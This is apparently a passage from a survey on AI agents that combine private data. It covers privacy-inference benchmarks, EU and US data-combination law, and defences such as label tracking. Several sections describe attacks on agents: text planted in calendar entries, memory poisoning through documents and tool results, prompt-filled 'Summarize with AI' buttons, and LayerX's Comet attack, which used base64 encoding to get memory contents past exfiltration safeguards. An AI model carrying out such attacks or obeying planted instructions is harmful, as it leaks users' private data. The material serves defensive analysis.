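AppOmni recommends putting agents on separate teams by task, so that an agent that reads strangers' text can't call one with powerful tools. This combination rule for tools wouldn't help if a user asked the record-management agent itself to deal with the malicious ticket, because that agent can both read and change tickets. AppOmni also recommends human approval for powerful tools, and sells a product that monitors ServiceNow agents for attacks of this kind.

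### Inference without an attacker

A Chinese wall can enforce only the conflicts that someone has listed. Several recent experiments tested whether agents would combine sources that look harmless on their own and reveal sensitive conclusions that nobody had listed. According to *Agents That Know Too Much* (2026), a survey of privacy research, checks on individual steps address this kind of leak less than any other.

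*Agent Tools Orchestration Leaks More* (Qiao, Liu and colleagues, 2025) describes an agent that prepares an employee's weekly expense report. The bank statement shows a restaurant charge, and the calendar shows a matching lunch with Jason M. The contacts list identifies him as a recruiter for a competitor, and the employee's search history includes "non-compete validity". The agent concludes that the employee may be looking for another job and includes this in a report that goes to the employee's manager.

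The team built 1,000 synthetic cases of this kind, in which two to five tool results together supported a sensitive conclusion but no single result did. In each case, the agent chose from six tools, received prepared results from those it chose, and wrote an answer. The cases involved no attacker, and no task required the conclusion. Across six models, agents completed 98.0% of the tasks on average and disclosed the sensitive conclusion in 88.6% of cases.

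Privacy instructions barely improved a score that combined task completion with non-disclosure. On a separate set of 500 cases, they raised the score by an average of 5.0 points, while training a model on safer answers raised it by 16.2 points.

Qiao and colleagues acknowledge that the 88.6% rate is weak evidence of how often this happens in real use, since they designed each case so that every tool result the agent needed also contained a piece of the secret. This design makes the benchmark a hard test for a Chinese wall. A rule against joining the bank statement and the calendar would keep the job search private, but it would also stop the agent from matching the restaurant charge to the lunch.

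### Facts from separate conversations

An agent with a long-term memory can join facts that its user mentioned weeks apart. *Can Agents Keep Secrets They Were Never Told?* (Yang, Yang and colleagues, 2026) tests this with 288 synthetic cases. In one of them, a user mentions the date of the next payment in one conversation, and other conversations indirectly reveal that the payment is for rent arrears at a particular neighbourhood centre. The user later asks the agent for a message to the letting desk about changing the payment date, and the message doesn't need to mention the arrears.

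The team tested six memory systems with the same small model, Qwen3.5-9B. They ran each case three times and counted a disclosure if at least two answers stated the complete secret. The disclosure rate ranged from 5.9% to 13.9%, even though the model had instructions not to volunteer private facts that the task didn't need. When the model received the full conversations instead of selected memories, the rate was 22.9%.

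Removing the links between facts reduced disclosures even when the facts stayed visible. The team used unrelated labels in place of the names and reference codes that connected records. In 207 cases where the service, place and date remained visible, disclosures fell from 16.4% to 7.7% with the memory system A-Mem and from 15.0% to 1.9% with MemGPT. A filter that only checks individual records for sensitive words would miss this difference.

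The team also compared several defences across nearly all the cases:

| Defence | Disclosures, A-Mem | Disclosures, MemGPT | Tasks completed, A-Mem | Tasks completed, MemGPT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None added | 13.9% | 11.1% | 20.1% | 18.1% |
| Stronger privacy instructions | 13.2% | 5.9% | 20.2% | 20.9% |
| Links between records removed | 5.6% | 1.4% | 19.2% | 20.6% |
| Personal details masked | 0% | 0% | 5.2% | 7.0% |
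| Only one record retrieved | 0% | 0% | 13.2% | 16.0% |
| A second model filters the answer | 0% | 0.3% | 27.8% | 28.1% |

Retrieving only one record is a crude combination rule. It worked without anyone having to list the conflicts, because the agent never had enough pieces in its context to combine. The agent also completed fewer tasks, since some needed more than one record.

The output filter seems to improve both results, but some tasks counted as complete only if the answer left out unrelated personal information, which the filter removed. The filter also received information about what each task permitted, which a real product might not have. Removing links made the answers less helpful on tasks that depended on the content of the records, but the completion rates do not reflect this.

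The low completion rates mean the agents were not very useful to begin with. Yang and colleagues found disclosures with six other models, but the largest of these had only 31 billion parameters. Other language models graded the answers, and people have not yet checked those grades systematically.

### Secrets pieced together from search queries

Data can also be combined outside the agent. Someone who sees all of the agent's web searches, such as a search provider, may be able to piece together private information from them. *MosaicLeaks* (Gurung, Gella and colleagues, 2026) studied this with 1,001 research tasks, most of which required both private company documents and public web pages.

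In one example, an agent searches twice for the growth in Lee's Market's online traffic in 2020. It finds the answer, 15%, in a private document, then uses that number in a web search for the next question. An observer who sees all three searches can guess that the company's traffic grew by 15%.

The researchers gave the agent's searches to a second model and asked it to infer private facts. With Qwen3-4B-Instruct as the agent, the second model recovered at least part of a private fact in 34.0% of tasks. When the researchers trained the agent only to do better research, it solved 59.3% of tasks, up from 48.7%, but leaks rose to 51.8% of tasks, partly because the agent searched more. Training it for privacy as well reduced leaks to 6.5%, and it still solved 58.1% of tasks. Its searches named the company much less often and contained fewer exact percentages.

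The rates include secrets that a single search revealed, so they don't measure aggregation alone. They also depend on which model judges the leaks. On 100 of the tasks, Claude Opus 4.7 found leaks from the privacy-trained agent in 14.3%, about twice as many as the model used in the main tests found. Gurung and colleagues consider their setup close to a worst case, because the observer sees every search in order, with no other users' searches mixed in. But nobody had to plant text or break into anything, because the agent sent the clues itself during ordinary work.

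### Questions to several agents

Someone can also collect the pieces deliberately by questioning several agents. *The Sum Leaks More Than Its Parts* (Patil, Stengel-Eskin and Bansal, 2025) gives an example in which one agent has access to John's customer number, another to each customer's purchases, and a third to the health conditions that appear in insurance claims. An attacker who questions all three can learn that John bought a blood pressure monitor but has no diagnosed heart condition, and infer that he is worried about his heart.

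The team tested 119 scenarios that paired such attacks with harmless requests that also needed answers from several agents. The attacker received a correct plan for which questions to ask, so the results show what happens when the attacker already knows where to look. The team compared several defences:

| Defence | Attacks blocked, Qwen3-32B | Harmless requests answered, Qwen3-32B | Attacks blocked, GPT-5 | Harmless requests answered, GPT-5 |
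|---|---|---|---|---|
| Each agent reasons about its own data | 31.1% | 68.9% | 70.5% | 63.6% |
| It also has a list of sensitive combinations and past questions | 29.8% | 64.4% | 92.1% | 64.0% |
| It also estimates what the questioner knows | 88.8% | 57.1% | 94.2% | 61.6% |
| Each agent votes several times, and one objection blocks the answer | 97.1% | 57.4% | 81.1% | 65.6% |
| Agents share their histories and vote, and one objection blocks the answer | 86.5% | 70.2% | 88.0% | 66.3% |

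Patil and colleagues favour the last defence, in which the agents share what they have already told the questioner. Agents using it answered more harmless requests than those using the other strong defences, but it didn't always give the best balance between blocking attacks and answering harmless requests. With GPT-5, using the list and a record of past questions blocked more attacks, and the agents answered only slightly fewer harmless requests. With the same information, the weaker Qwen model blocked fewer than a third of attacks.

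The shared histories serve much the same purpose as Brewer and Nash's record of who has read what, but language models decide how to use them. Since the agents' facts were in tables and the sensitive combinations were already on a list, ordinary code could have kept the record and blocked the release of the last piece of any listed combination. The team didn't test this. Such code would give the same answer every time, but it would miss any combination that wasn't on the list, and an attacker could get around it by using two accounts that the software treated as different people.

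## Legal limits on combining personal data

A combination rule needs a list of things that must stay apart. In most of the systems above, a company's own staff had to write that list, but for personal data, legislators have written part of it. The European Union's *General Data Protection Regulation* (2016), or GDPR, limits the use of personal data for new purposes and restricts some kinds, such as health records, much more tightly. The EU's *Digital Markets Act* (2022), or DMA, stops the largest online platforms from combining people's data across services without consent. In the US, the Computer Matching and Privacy Protection Act of 1988 sets conditions that federal agencies must meet before they compare certain records.

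| Rule | Who has to follow it | What triggers it | What lifts it |
|---|---|---|---|
| GDPR, purpose limitation | Whoever decides why and how to use personal data | A use other than the one the data was collected for | A compatible purpose, consent, or legislation that permits the use |
| GDPR, special categories | The same | Data that reveals health, religion, politics or certain other matters | Explicit consent or one of nine other exceptions |
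| DMA, Article 5(2) | Platforms that the European Commission has designated as gatekeepers | Combining personal data from different services, or using one service's data in another | Consent to that specific choice, or a few grounds such as a legal duty |
| Computer Matching Act | US federal agencies and the bodies that match records with them | A computerized comparison for certain purposes, mainly to check who is entitled to benefits | A written agreement, with further duties before an agency acts on a match |

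### Using data for a new purpose

The GDPR covers any information about an identifiable person. It binds the controller, the person or organization that decides why and how to use the data. Joining two sets of personal data counts as processing, because the GDPR's definition of processing includes "alignment or combination". The controller therefore needs one of six legal grounds for the join, such as consent, a contract or a legal duty.

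Article 5(1)(b) adds purpose limitation. A controller must collect data for "specified, explicit and legitimate purposes" and may not go on to use it in a way that is incompatible with them. If neither consent nor legislation covers the new use, Article 6(4) requires the controller to consider at least five things:

- any link between the original purpose and the new one
- the context in which the controller collected the data, especially its relationship with the people concerned
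- the nature of the data, especially whether it falls into a special category or concerns criminal offences
- the possible consequences for those people
- safeguards, such as encryption or replacing names with codes

The article gives these factors no weights, and the list is open-ended, so two careful lawyers could disagree about the same case. Archiving in the public interest, research and statistics count as compatible purposes if the controller applies the required safeguards.

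Suppose the payroll firm is in the EU and wants its agent to join the payroll file with the sickness records. The firm needs both to work out sick pay, and the GDPR has an exception for health data that an employer needs to meet its duties under employment law. If the firm wanted to use the joined data to choose whom to make redundant, it would probably fail the test, because employees gave it the records for a different reason and the consequences for them would be serious. The files, the agent and the head of personnel who reads the table are the same in both cases, so a Chinese Wall policy or a connector group would have to allow both joins or block both, because neither takes the purpose into account.

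An organization can weaken this protection by describing its purposes vaguely. If the stated purpose is "to assist staff", almost any combination of data fits. The UK's data protection regulator, the Information Commissioner's Office (ICO), published a report on agents in January 2026. Its chapter *Data protection and privacy risks* describes a risk that organizations will set purposes broadly enough to cover everything an agent might do. The ICO wants a specific purpose for each stage of processing, including for information an agent collects while it runs. It also expects that agents may reuse information an organization collected for something else.

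A clear purpose also determines how much data the agent may have. The GDPR's data minimisation principle, which UK law shares, limits personal data to what is necessary for the purpose. The ICO concludes that organizations should not give an agent access to information "just because it might be useful in the future". In Qiao and colleagues' expense-report example, the agent drew on the employee's search history. An employer would struggle to show that a real expense report requires that history, and without it the agent would have had less reason to suspect that the employee was looking for a job.

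The people the ICO consulted disagreed about how much data an agent should be able to access. Many wanted users to choose in advance which data it may use for a given purpose, perhaps allowing more access once it had proved reliable. Others preferred to give it broad access from the start, because context helps it perform better and personalise its results. The ICO accepts that the second group has a practical point, but not that it changes the law. It says it is unclear which technical measures will eventually satisfy both.

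The ICO did not intend the report as guidance or formal regulatory expectations, according to Inside Privacy, a blog by the law firm Covington. The report presents the ICO's early thinking, and most of the risks it describes are predictions rather than findings about particular products. The ICO planned to update its guidance on automated decisions, starting with public consultations in 2026, and to produce a code of practice on AI.

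### How ordinary data becomes health data

Article 9 of the GDPR prohibits processing data that reveals racial or ethnic origin, political opinions, religious or philosophical beliefs, or trade union membership. The ban also covers genetic data, biometric data used to identify someone, and data about health, sex life or sexual orientation. A controller that wants to use such data needs one of the ten exceptions in Article 9 as well as an ordinary legal ground. The exceptions include explicit consent, employment law, legal claims, medical care and data that the person has clearly made public.

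The GDPR's special categories of data don't include salary, debts or plans to change jobs. The job search in Qiao and colleagues' example and the rent arrears in Yang and colleagues' would therefore get only the GDPR's general protection, even if the people concerned wanted to keep them private.

It is less obvious when Article 9 applies to data that doesn't mention any of these subjects. The Court of Justice of the European Union addressed this question in *Meta Platforms Inc. v Bundeskartellamt* (2023). Meta collected data on Facebook users' visits to other companies' websites and apps, and on their use of its other services, such as Instagram. It linked this "off-Facebook data" to their Facebook accounts and used the resulting profiles to target advertising. In 2019 Germany's competition authority, the Bundeskartellamt, prohibited Meta from doing this to private users in Germany without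 their consent. Meta challenged the decision, and a court in Düsseldorf asked the Court of Justice how to interpret the GDPR.

The Court held that Meta was processing special category data when it recorded a visit to, say, a gay dating site or a health site, if the processing could reveal information in one of those categories. The national court had to check whether the data could do so, "on their own" or when linked to the users' accounts. A visit might be enough even if the user typed nothing into the site.

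The Court added that the prohibition applies whether or not the information is correct, and whether or not the company was trying to obtain it. An assistant that, unasked, wrongly concludes from a woman's orders that she is pregnant may therefore have processed data about her health.

Linking creates a difficulty for the labels in systems such as FIDES. Suppose each source has a label that lists its categories of data. The obvious way to label a combination is to take every category that appears in either source, but that can miss a category that arises only from the link:

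```
simple label:   categories(A + B) = categories(A) ∪ categories(B)
linked data:    categories(A + B) may include a category found in neither A nor B
```

For example, a calendar entry for "Dr. Smith" and a location inside a medical building could together suggest a medical appointment. Software would have to assess the data again once combined, or someone would have to list the pair in advance.

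The scope of the judgment is unsettled. The websites in the case concerned the special categories directly, so inferring a person's health or sexuality from a visit took little guesswork. But a capable model could guess at someone's health from almost any large collection of their purchases or messages. If a faint possibility of such an inference were enough, Article 9 would cover most of what a personal assistant reads. A company could reasonably argue that Article 9 doesn't apply when the inference is speculative, but it would be taking a legal risk.

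The Court also held that if a company collects sensitive and ordinary data in bulk and cannot separate the items at the time of collection, a single sensitive item brings the whole set under the prohibition unless an exception applies. Most mailboxes contain at least one message about somebody's health. An assistant that copies the entire mailbox is therefore in a weaker position than one that fetches only the messages it needs, because the second can avoid collecting the health messages.

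The ICO raises the same concern about agents, warning that an agent may infer special category data and use it in a decision even when its stated purpose involves none. It advises organizations to assess this possibility beforehand. If the agent could make such inferences, they need a legal ground and an Article 9 exception, and must tell people that it may happen. Alternatively, they can restrict the agent's ability to make these inferences by technical means, which the ICO doesn't specify.

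### Matching government records in the US

The American law is narrower than the GDPR and mainly imposes procedural requirements. According to the Congressional Research Service's *Federal Data Integration and Individual Rights*, the law covers comparisons of records to establish or verify eligibility for federal benefits and to recover debts and improper payments under benefit programs. It also covers some comparisons involving federal personnel or payroll records. Before 1988, nobody knew how much record matching federal agencies were doing, and people had too little protection when an agency acted against them on inaccurate information.

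The 1988 law amended the *Privacy Act of 1974*, which restricts how agencies disclose records about individuals. The 1988 law defines a matching program as a computerized comparison of two or more automated systems of records, or of one such system with non-federal records, for a listed purpose. Checking eligibility is one of those purposes, so an agency that pays a housing benefit would be running a matching program if it compared its recipients with a state's wage records to find people who earn too much to qualify.

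The Department of Justice's *Computer Matching Agreements and Notices* quotes the central rule, which, with some exceptions, forbids an agency to disclose records for matching without a written agreement with the body that receives them. The Congressional Research Service's *Computer Matching and Privacy Protection* describes the law's other requirements. A data integrity board in each participating agency must approve the agreement, which must be available to the public. An agency must notify people that it uses their information for matching. Before it stops or reduces anyone's payments because of a match, it must verify the information and give the person a chance to contest it.

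None of this requires the individual's consent. The law treats some matching as legitimate and focuses on making it visible and catching errors. That is a sensible approach to an agent's ordinary mistakes. An agent that confuses two people with the same name will produce a false match, just as the payroll agent confused the finance director with a recruiter. Verification gives a person a chance to notice the mistake before someone loses their rent money.

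The law may not cover every agent that works with government records. Its definition of a matching program concerns comparisons of systems of records. A caseworker's agent might look up a single applicant in two systems without comparing the systems as a whole, and a lawyer would have to decide whether that counts. Comparisons for other purposes fall outside the 1988 provisions, though the Privacy Act's general limits still apply. One exception to those limits allows disclosure for a "routine use", meaning a use compatible with the purpose of collection, so agencies have to make much the same judgment as controllers do under Article 6(4).

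AISP's *A Privacy Act Primer* (2025), a brief from a research group at the University of Pennsylvania, describes a dispute about these limits. Executive Order 14243 directed federal agencies to secure "unfettered access" to comprehensive data from every state program that receives federal money. The Department of Agriculture then demanded data on recipients of food assistance from states and the companies that process the payments. By June 2025, when the brief was written, privacy advocates had gone to court, arguing that both the order and the demand violated the Privacy Act.

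### Gatekeepers and the consent they need

Of the three laws, the DMA comes closest to an explicit rule on combining data. It binds gatekeepers, which are companies that the European Commission has designated because businesses depend on them to reach customers. The Commission presumes that a company qualifies if it meets thresholds that include at least 45 million monthly users and 10,000 yearly business users in the EU, and either €7.5 billion in annual EU turnover or a market value of €75 billion. The obligations apply only to the services that the Commission lists in its designation decision, such as a search engine, a marketplace or a social network.

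Virtual assistants are a type of service that the Commission can list. The DMA defines them as software that processes requests, including written ones, and on that basis provides access to other services or controls connected devices. Many agents seem to fit this definition. Article 5(2) can also matter to an unlisted assistant, because it restricts what a gatekeeper does elsewhere with data from its listed services.

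Without consent, a gatekeeper may not:

- use personal data from other companies' services that run on its platform for online advertising
- combine personal data from a listed service with personal data from any of its other services or from third parties
- use personal data from a listed service in a service that it provides separately, or the reverse
- sign users in to its other services in order to combine their data

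The third prohibition is especially relevant to agents. An assistant that consults someone's shopping history while drafting their mail is using one service's data in another, even if it never builds a merged profile and discards its context after each task. The prohibition also covers data that isn't sensitive, such as a list of books.

The ban doesn't apply if a gatekeeper offers the user the specific choice and gets consent that meets the GDPR's standard. The gatekeeper can also rely on three of the GDPR's other legal grounds: a legal duty, someone's vital interests, or a task in the public interest. The DMA doesn't list the two grounds companies would probably find most convenient, a contract with the user and the company's own legitimate interests. If a user refuses or withdraws consent, the gatekeeper may not repeat its request for the same purpose more than once within a year.

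The Court of Justice set similar limits on Meta under the GDPR, ten months after the EU adopted the DMA. Meta had argued that it needed the linked data to fulfil its contract with Facebook's users. The Court replied that processing must be "objectively indispensable" to the contract, not just useful. It doubted that personalised content met this standard. It also doubted that smooth movement between Meta's services did, since people can use Facebook without Instagram. The Court further ruled that Meta could not rely on legitimate interests to personalise advertising without consent. A company that wants to combine data to improve its assistant's answers would face the same objection.

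The remaining legal basis was consent. The Court held that users can validly consent even when a company dominates its market, but that the company's power is an important reason to doubt whether they were free to refuse. Users must be able to refuse individual processing operations that the contract doesn't require and still use the service. The company may have to offer an equivalent version without those operations, for an appropriate fee if necessary. Because users couldn't reasonably expect Meta to process data about their activity outside Facebook, the Court also considered it appropriate for them to be able to consent separately to the use of Facebook data and off-Facebook data. If they couldn't, the national court had to presume that their consent to the use of off-Facebook data was not freely given. Meta had the burden of proving that users consented freely.

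### An authorization check for mail and shopping history

The following hypothetical check illustrates how a policy engine might apply Article 5(2) of the DMA, and is not legal advice. An imaginary gatekeeper runs a marketplace, which is a listed service, and a mail service. Its assistant can read both, and the company wants the assistant to suggest presents for the people a user writes to. The check also flags special category data, because the company must also comply with the GDPR.

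| Purpose | Consent record | Data categories | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Recommend products in the marketplace | Shopping history, for recommendations | Purchases | No combination, so this check doesn't apply |
| Suggest presents | Mail, for sorting messages; shopping history, for recommendations | Messages and purchases | Ask the user |
| Suggest presents | User refused two months ago | Messages and purchases | Block, and don't ask again yet |
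| Suggest presents | Mail and shopping history together, for suggesting presents | Messages and purchases | Allow |
| Suggest presents | The same | Also a friend's message about her pregnancy | Block, and refer the case to a lawyer |

In the second row, the user has agreed to the assistant's use of each source but not to the join. A simple program might check for two permissions, find both and go ahead, which is how OAuth scopes normally work. The consent that the company needs is a different record:

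```
on record:  {mail} for sorting messages
            {shopping history} for recommendations
needed:     {mail, shopping history} for suggesting presents
```

Under the GDPR, consent must be specific and informed, and combining two sources of data can reveal things that neither does alone. A message confirming "your appointment on Thursday" and an order for vitamins could each have many explanations, but together they may suggest a pregnancy. Someone who agreed to the use of each source for its own purpose had no reason to consider what the two would reveal together. Adding both scopes to one consent screen probably wouldn't solve the problem, because the screen would show what the assistant can read but not that the company will combine the data, or why.

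Code can do many of these checks. It can look up whether the marketplace is a listed service, whether a consent record names both sources and the purpose, whether the user has withdrawn consent, and when the company last asked for it. Each check compares stored values, so the result doesn't depend on the model's output.

The stored values have to come from a reliable source, though. If the model supplies the purpose of each request, it can mistakenly supply one that passes. Text planted in an email could also instruct it to give the purpose as "suggest presents", or claim that the user has already agreed. The feature that started the task should therefore set the purpose, and only the user's settings should change the consent record. Even then, the check can't confirm that the assistant uses the data only for that purpose once the data is in its context.

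Other parts need a lawyer. A program can find a consent record but can't determine whether the user was free to refuse, or whether the wording explained the join clearly enough. It can compare two purposes character by character but can't judge whether "suggest presents" is specific enough. The limit on repeated requests is also open to interpretation. The illustration uses the cautious reading, that the company should wait a year after a refusal, but a company might read the text as allowing one earlier repeat.

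It is harder to tell whether a user's direct request counts as consent. If someone types "which of my orders hasn't arrived?", the assistant has to compare the courier's emails with the shopping history. The request is a clear, deliberate act, and most people would be annoyed by a consent form. But the DMA also requires the company to have presented the user with a specific choice, and it isn't obvious that answering the user's question does that. The company's lawyers could decide this once for a whole class of requests, and code could then apply their decision.

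The last row of the table is the most difficult. Software can look for messages about health, but it will miss some, and it is even less able to recognise a condition that is revealed only when the data is combined. The user's consent can't solve the problem either, because the friend is the one who is pregnant. The Court held that Article 9 applies whether the information concerns the platform's user or anyone else, and explicit consent must come from the person the data is about. The friend has never dealt with the assistant and may not know it exists.

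## What an agent may keep: memory, retention and lost labels

An assistant that reads a message from the user's friend about her pregnancy may save a note that she is expecting a baby in May. When the user asks for present ideas weeks later, the assistant loads the note without opening the message, so a check on the mailbox no longer applies. Unless the software saved a label with the note, nothing marks it as health data about someone who never gave consent.

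Any rule that depends on labels has this weakness once an agent can store data. Storage also raises the question of how long the agent may keep the data.

### Where an agent leaves data

| Place | How data gets there | How it comes back |
|---|---|---|
| Context | Every message and tool result adds text | The model receives it at each step until the session ends or the software shortens it |
| Long-term memory | The model, or a separate program that watches the conversation, saves facts and preferences | Software loads all the entries or searches for relevant ones |
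| Files and notes | The agent writes them during a task | A later task opens them |
| Calendars, tickets and other apps | A tool call creates an entry | The app returns it along with the user's own entries |
| Caches | Software keeps copies of results to save time | The software uses the copy instead of fetching the original again |
| Logs | The agent's software and the model's provider record requests and results | Someone reads them during an investigation, or asks an agent to |

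Deleting an item from one of these places usually leaves copies in others. If a user deletes an email, a memory the agent made from it and the log of the tool call that fetched it may both remain.

### A calendar entry that looks like the user's own

In the FIDES example of a meeting request, the agent takes the details from a stranger's email and creates a calendar event. Commenting on this design by Costa and colleagues, Jason Rebholz of the company Evoke Security points out that the event's description could contain planted text. When the user later asks for a summary of the day's meetings, the agent makes a fresh plan and trusts the calendar because it belongs to the user:

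```
Monday:   stranger's email (untrusted) -> event description (untrusted) -> calendar
Tuesday:  calendar -> event description (trusted)
```

The calendar stored the text without its label, so the text gets past Meta's Rule of Two just as a saved copy of the survey page does. The agent's software could prevent this by keeping a separate record of each event's label and treating any event without a record as untrusted. That default would also cover invitations that strangers send directly.

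Xie, Zhu and colleagues (2026), in *What If Prompt Injection Never Left?*, measured how well attacks survive the end of a session. They built 486 cases in shopping, travel and finance for an agent with a memory, a file system and 14 tools. In each case, the agent received an adversarial request and could save data. The researchers then ended the session, discarded the conversation but kept the stored data, and gave a new session a harmless request.

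Across five models, 41.9% of the attacks succeeded in the second session. The agent stored the attacker's material in 77.4% of cases, and most of what it stored entered the later context. False facts succeeded more often than false preferences (73.6% against 6.8%). The attacker's text arrived in a request to the agent, so these rates may be higher than for text in an email the agent happens to read.

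### Planting a memory through a document

*Hidden in Memory* (Pulipaka, Hlebik and colleagues, 2026) tests the more common situation, in which a user gives an assistant a document that someone else has altered. The attacker wants the assistant to save a false memory about the user, such as a preference for uploading exported files to a certain address. The attacker can't see the memory store and doesn't take part in later conversations.

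The team paired 700 documents with false memories. Of these, 500 memories aimed to change what the assistant says and 200 aimed to change what it does. One model wrote a reusable attack text, and another explained why failed versions hadn't worked, so that the first could improve them. In separate sessions, the team then tested whether the assistant retrieved false memories and acted on them. These are the results when the assistant itself decided what to save:

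| Model | Saved false memories meant to change answers | Saved false memories meant to change actions | Acted on the memory in a related task, once retrieved |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4 | 99.4% | 97.0% | 83% |
| GPT-5.5 | 99.8% | 91.5% | 79% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 64.2% | 6.5% | 60% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 88.6% | 67.0% | 89% |
| Kimi K2.6 | 95.0% | 81.0% | 82% |
| DeepSeek V4 Pro | 96.2% | 88.5% | 80% |

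The complete attack has to pass all three stages. For memories meant to change actions, it succeeded in 3.0% to 66.0% of related tasks, depending on the model, and in at most 5.0% of unrelated ones. A false memory about file uploads mostly has no effect until the user asks the agent to export a file.

How the software presented documents and memories also made a large difference. GPT-5.5 saved fewer false memories when the team used setups modelled on Claude's or Gemini's. Better instructions helped, but not reliably. With one optimised set of instructions, Kimi K2.6 saved only 6.2% of the false memories meant to change answers. When the team adapted the attack to those instructions, the rate rose to 64.6%.

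The team also tried 25 attacks on each of three live websites. ChatGPT and Claude each saved the false memory 24 times, and Kimi saved it 22 times. These attacks had already worked in the main tests, so the results confirm that the problem exists in real products but don't estimate how often a new attempt would succeed. *Memory Poisoning Attack and Defense on Memory Based LLM-Agents* (2026) similarly notes that researchers had tested an older attack, with a reported injection rate above 95%, mostly in idealised or controlled settings.

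Companies are already trying to plant favorable memories in the public's AI assistants. Microsoft (2026) found 50 different prompts from 31 companies in 60 days of email traffic. Many were behind "Summarize with AI" buttons, which open an assistant with a prompt already filled in. The prompt contains a request for a summary and an instruction to remember the company as a trusted source. All 31 were real businesses promoting themselves. Microsoft counted attempts, and reports that their success varied between assistants and over time.

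Systems that label data by origin can mislabel the requests that the buttons create. The company wrote the request, but it arrives in the box where the user types, so a simple design would label it as trusted. Software could instead treat text from a link as untrusted until the user has read and submitted it.

A false memory can also come from an ordinary mistake. Suppose a user asks an agent to send one file to her home address because she is travelling, and the agent records that she prefers to receive files there. The ICO warns that inaccurate information in an agent's memory, whether acquired or invented, can affect many later decisions. An integrity label wouldn't flag this error, because the user's request was trusted. She might notice it if the agent showed her the proposed memory before saving it.

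### Copies that outlive the original

Yang, Bullwinkel and colleagues (2026), in *MemoryDojo*, followed a single piece of planted text through later tasks. They joined AgentDojo tasks into 155 sequences of sessions and ran them with five memory systems. In the main test, they added the text to one tool result in the first session and then left the agent alone. The table shows how often GPT-5.6 Luna carried out the attacker's goal in later tasks from the same field, such as banking:

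| Memory system | Later tasks affected, basic text | Later tasks affected, optimised text | Sequences affected at least once, optimised text |
|---|---|---|---|
| A-MEM | 21.0% | 44.0% | 71.0% |
| Graphiti | 7.8% | 9.3% | 30.1% |
| Letta | 15.3% | 46.3% | 50.5% |
| Mem0 | 7.9% | 21.0% | 39.8% |
| Memora | 20.4% | 29.8% | 66.7% |

Graphiti stored the planted text almost every time but retrieved it in only about a third of later sessions. Its search returns short facts about how things are related, which often omit the planted instruction. This format may explain much of Graphiti's resistance, though its designers may not have chosen it for security.

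The agent can create more copies by acting on a false entry. If it follows a false preference to forward invoices, the record of that session also goes into memory and later looks like an established practice. With the optimised text, 63% of the poisoned retrievals in A-MEM included at least one entry that the system had created or rewritten after the original attack. Deleting the original entry would have left those copies in place.

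Older memories can crowd out planted text. When the team first filled the memory with about 50 harmless conversations, the share of later tasks affected fell to between 0% and 5.3% in sequences that mixed several fields. But with Memora, the attack still worked at least once in 45% of runs. The benchmark doesn't compare defences. *From Untrusted Input to Trusted Memory* (2026) reports an average attack success rate of 50.46% on two agents and finds that existing prompt injection defences only partly cover memory attacks.

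### Taking memories out of Comet

Attackers can also steal what an agent remembers. Users can connect Comet, Perplexity's AI browser, to their email and calendar. *Is Perplexity Comet Safe?* (Gispan, 2025) describes how the security company LayerX used a web link to extract data that Comet had handled earlier, such as an email it had helped write.

The victim only had to open the link, which contained a question for the assistant and a setting for where to look for the answer. When the researchers gave that setting an unrecognised value, the assistant searched its memory instead of the web. The question included an instruction to send what it found to the attacker's server. Perplexity had safeguards against sending sensitive data directly, so the researchers had the assistant first convert the data to base64, a standard way of rewriting data as letters and digits. The safeguards didn't detect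 the converted data.

LayerX reported the attack on 27 August 2025. According to Gispan, Perplexity replied that it could not identify any security impact and marked the report "Not Applicable". LayerX published its findings on 4 October.

Encoding data in Base64 doesn't change who is allowed to read it. If Comet had kept a list of permitted readers with each memory, the encoded copy would have inherited the list, and a check against it would have blocked sending the copy to the attacker's server. That check would also have to run in trusted contexts, unlike the one in Microsoft's Teams policy, because the software might label the link's text as a request from the user.

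### SPA: storing the label with the data

*SPA* (Girrens and Wang, August 2026) describes an agent that keeps labels on everything it stores. In the paper's example, a user asks the agent on Monday to fetch an invoice from Acme and keep the details. An attacker has planted a false bank account and an instruction in the invoice. On Tuesday the user asks the agent to pay the invoice. The instruction could change Tuesday's plan if the planning model reads it, and the false account could receive the money even if the plan is correct.

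SPA assumes that an attacker may control some of the agent's tools, including their names and descriptions, as well as any content that other tools return. It trusts the user's requests and the company's security settings.

Like CaMeL, SPA writes a complete plan for each request before it runs any tools. The plan can use only six kinds of step: retrieve a stored item, call a tool, have an isolated model process text, show something to the user, choose between branches, and repeat steps for each item in a list. Ordinary code then works out the labels for the whole plan and rejects it if any tool call would break a rule. The planner can't revise a rejected plan, because repeated revisions based on the checker's feedback might eventually get an unsafe plan accepted.

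SPA stores each result with its value, its label and a description. The description gives the data's format, what it represents and which request produced it. The planner reads only the description. The planner wrote the important parts of it before the agent fetched anything, so text planted in the invoice can't get into the description. When a later plan retrieves the value, the original label comes back with it.

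If the company requires trusted input for payments, SPA handles the invoice like this:

| Step | Integrity of the data | Decision |
|---|---|---|
| Monday: fetch the invoice and store it | Untrusted | Allow |
| Tuesday: retrieve the invoice | Untrusted, as on Monday | Allow |
| Tuesday: have the isolated model extract the account number | Still untrusted | Allow |
| Tuesday: pay that account | Too low for the payment tool | Reject the plan before any step runs |

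The rule would also reject a genuine invoice. To pay it, the agent would need a way to endorse the account number, for example after code had matched it with the company's supplier list. Girrens and Wang leave endorsement for future work. The labels also wouldn't help if the agent retrieved the wrong one of two trusted invoices by mistake.

SPA also closes the leak that Garby and colleagues found in CaMeL, where a program revealed whether a balance was high by skipping an instruction. In SPA, every step inside a branch inherits the label of the branch's condition. A plan can set each variable only once, and a variable set inside a branch can't be used outside it, so SPA's language can't express that program.

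### What SPA's tests measure

AgentDojo resets the agent after each task, so it can't test attacks that wait in storage. Girrens and Wang split its tasks into sequences of two to five requests in which later requests need earlier results. They used GPT-5.4 nano and ran 949 attacks on each version of the agent:

| Version of SPA | Tasks completed without an attack, split tasks | Attacks that succeeded, split tasks | Tasks completed without an attack, original tasks | Attacks that succeeded, original tasks |
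|---|---|---|---|---|
| No label checks, and the planner sees stored values | 65.9% | 0.6% | Not tested | Not tested |
| No label checks | 62.5% | 0.3% | 53.0% | 0.4% |
| Label checks | 35.3% | 0.2% | 29.0% | 0.0% |

The label checks cut the number of completed tasks by almost half, mainly because many ordinary tasks use outside data in a consequential action. Attacks succeeded less than 1% of the time without the checks, so the test could show little benefit from them. Even showing stored text to the planner, which the design is meant to prevent, raised the attack success rate only to 0.6%. Girrens and Wang acknowledge that the attack they used is a weak test of delayed poisoning. The attacks by Pulipaka and colleagues would be a better test because they target memory directly.

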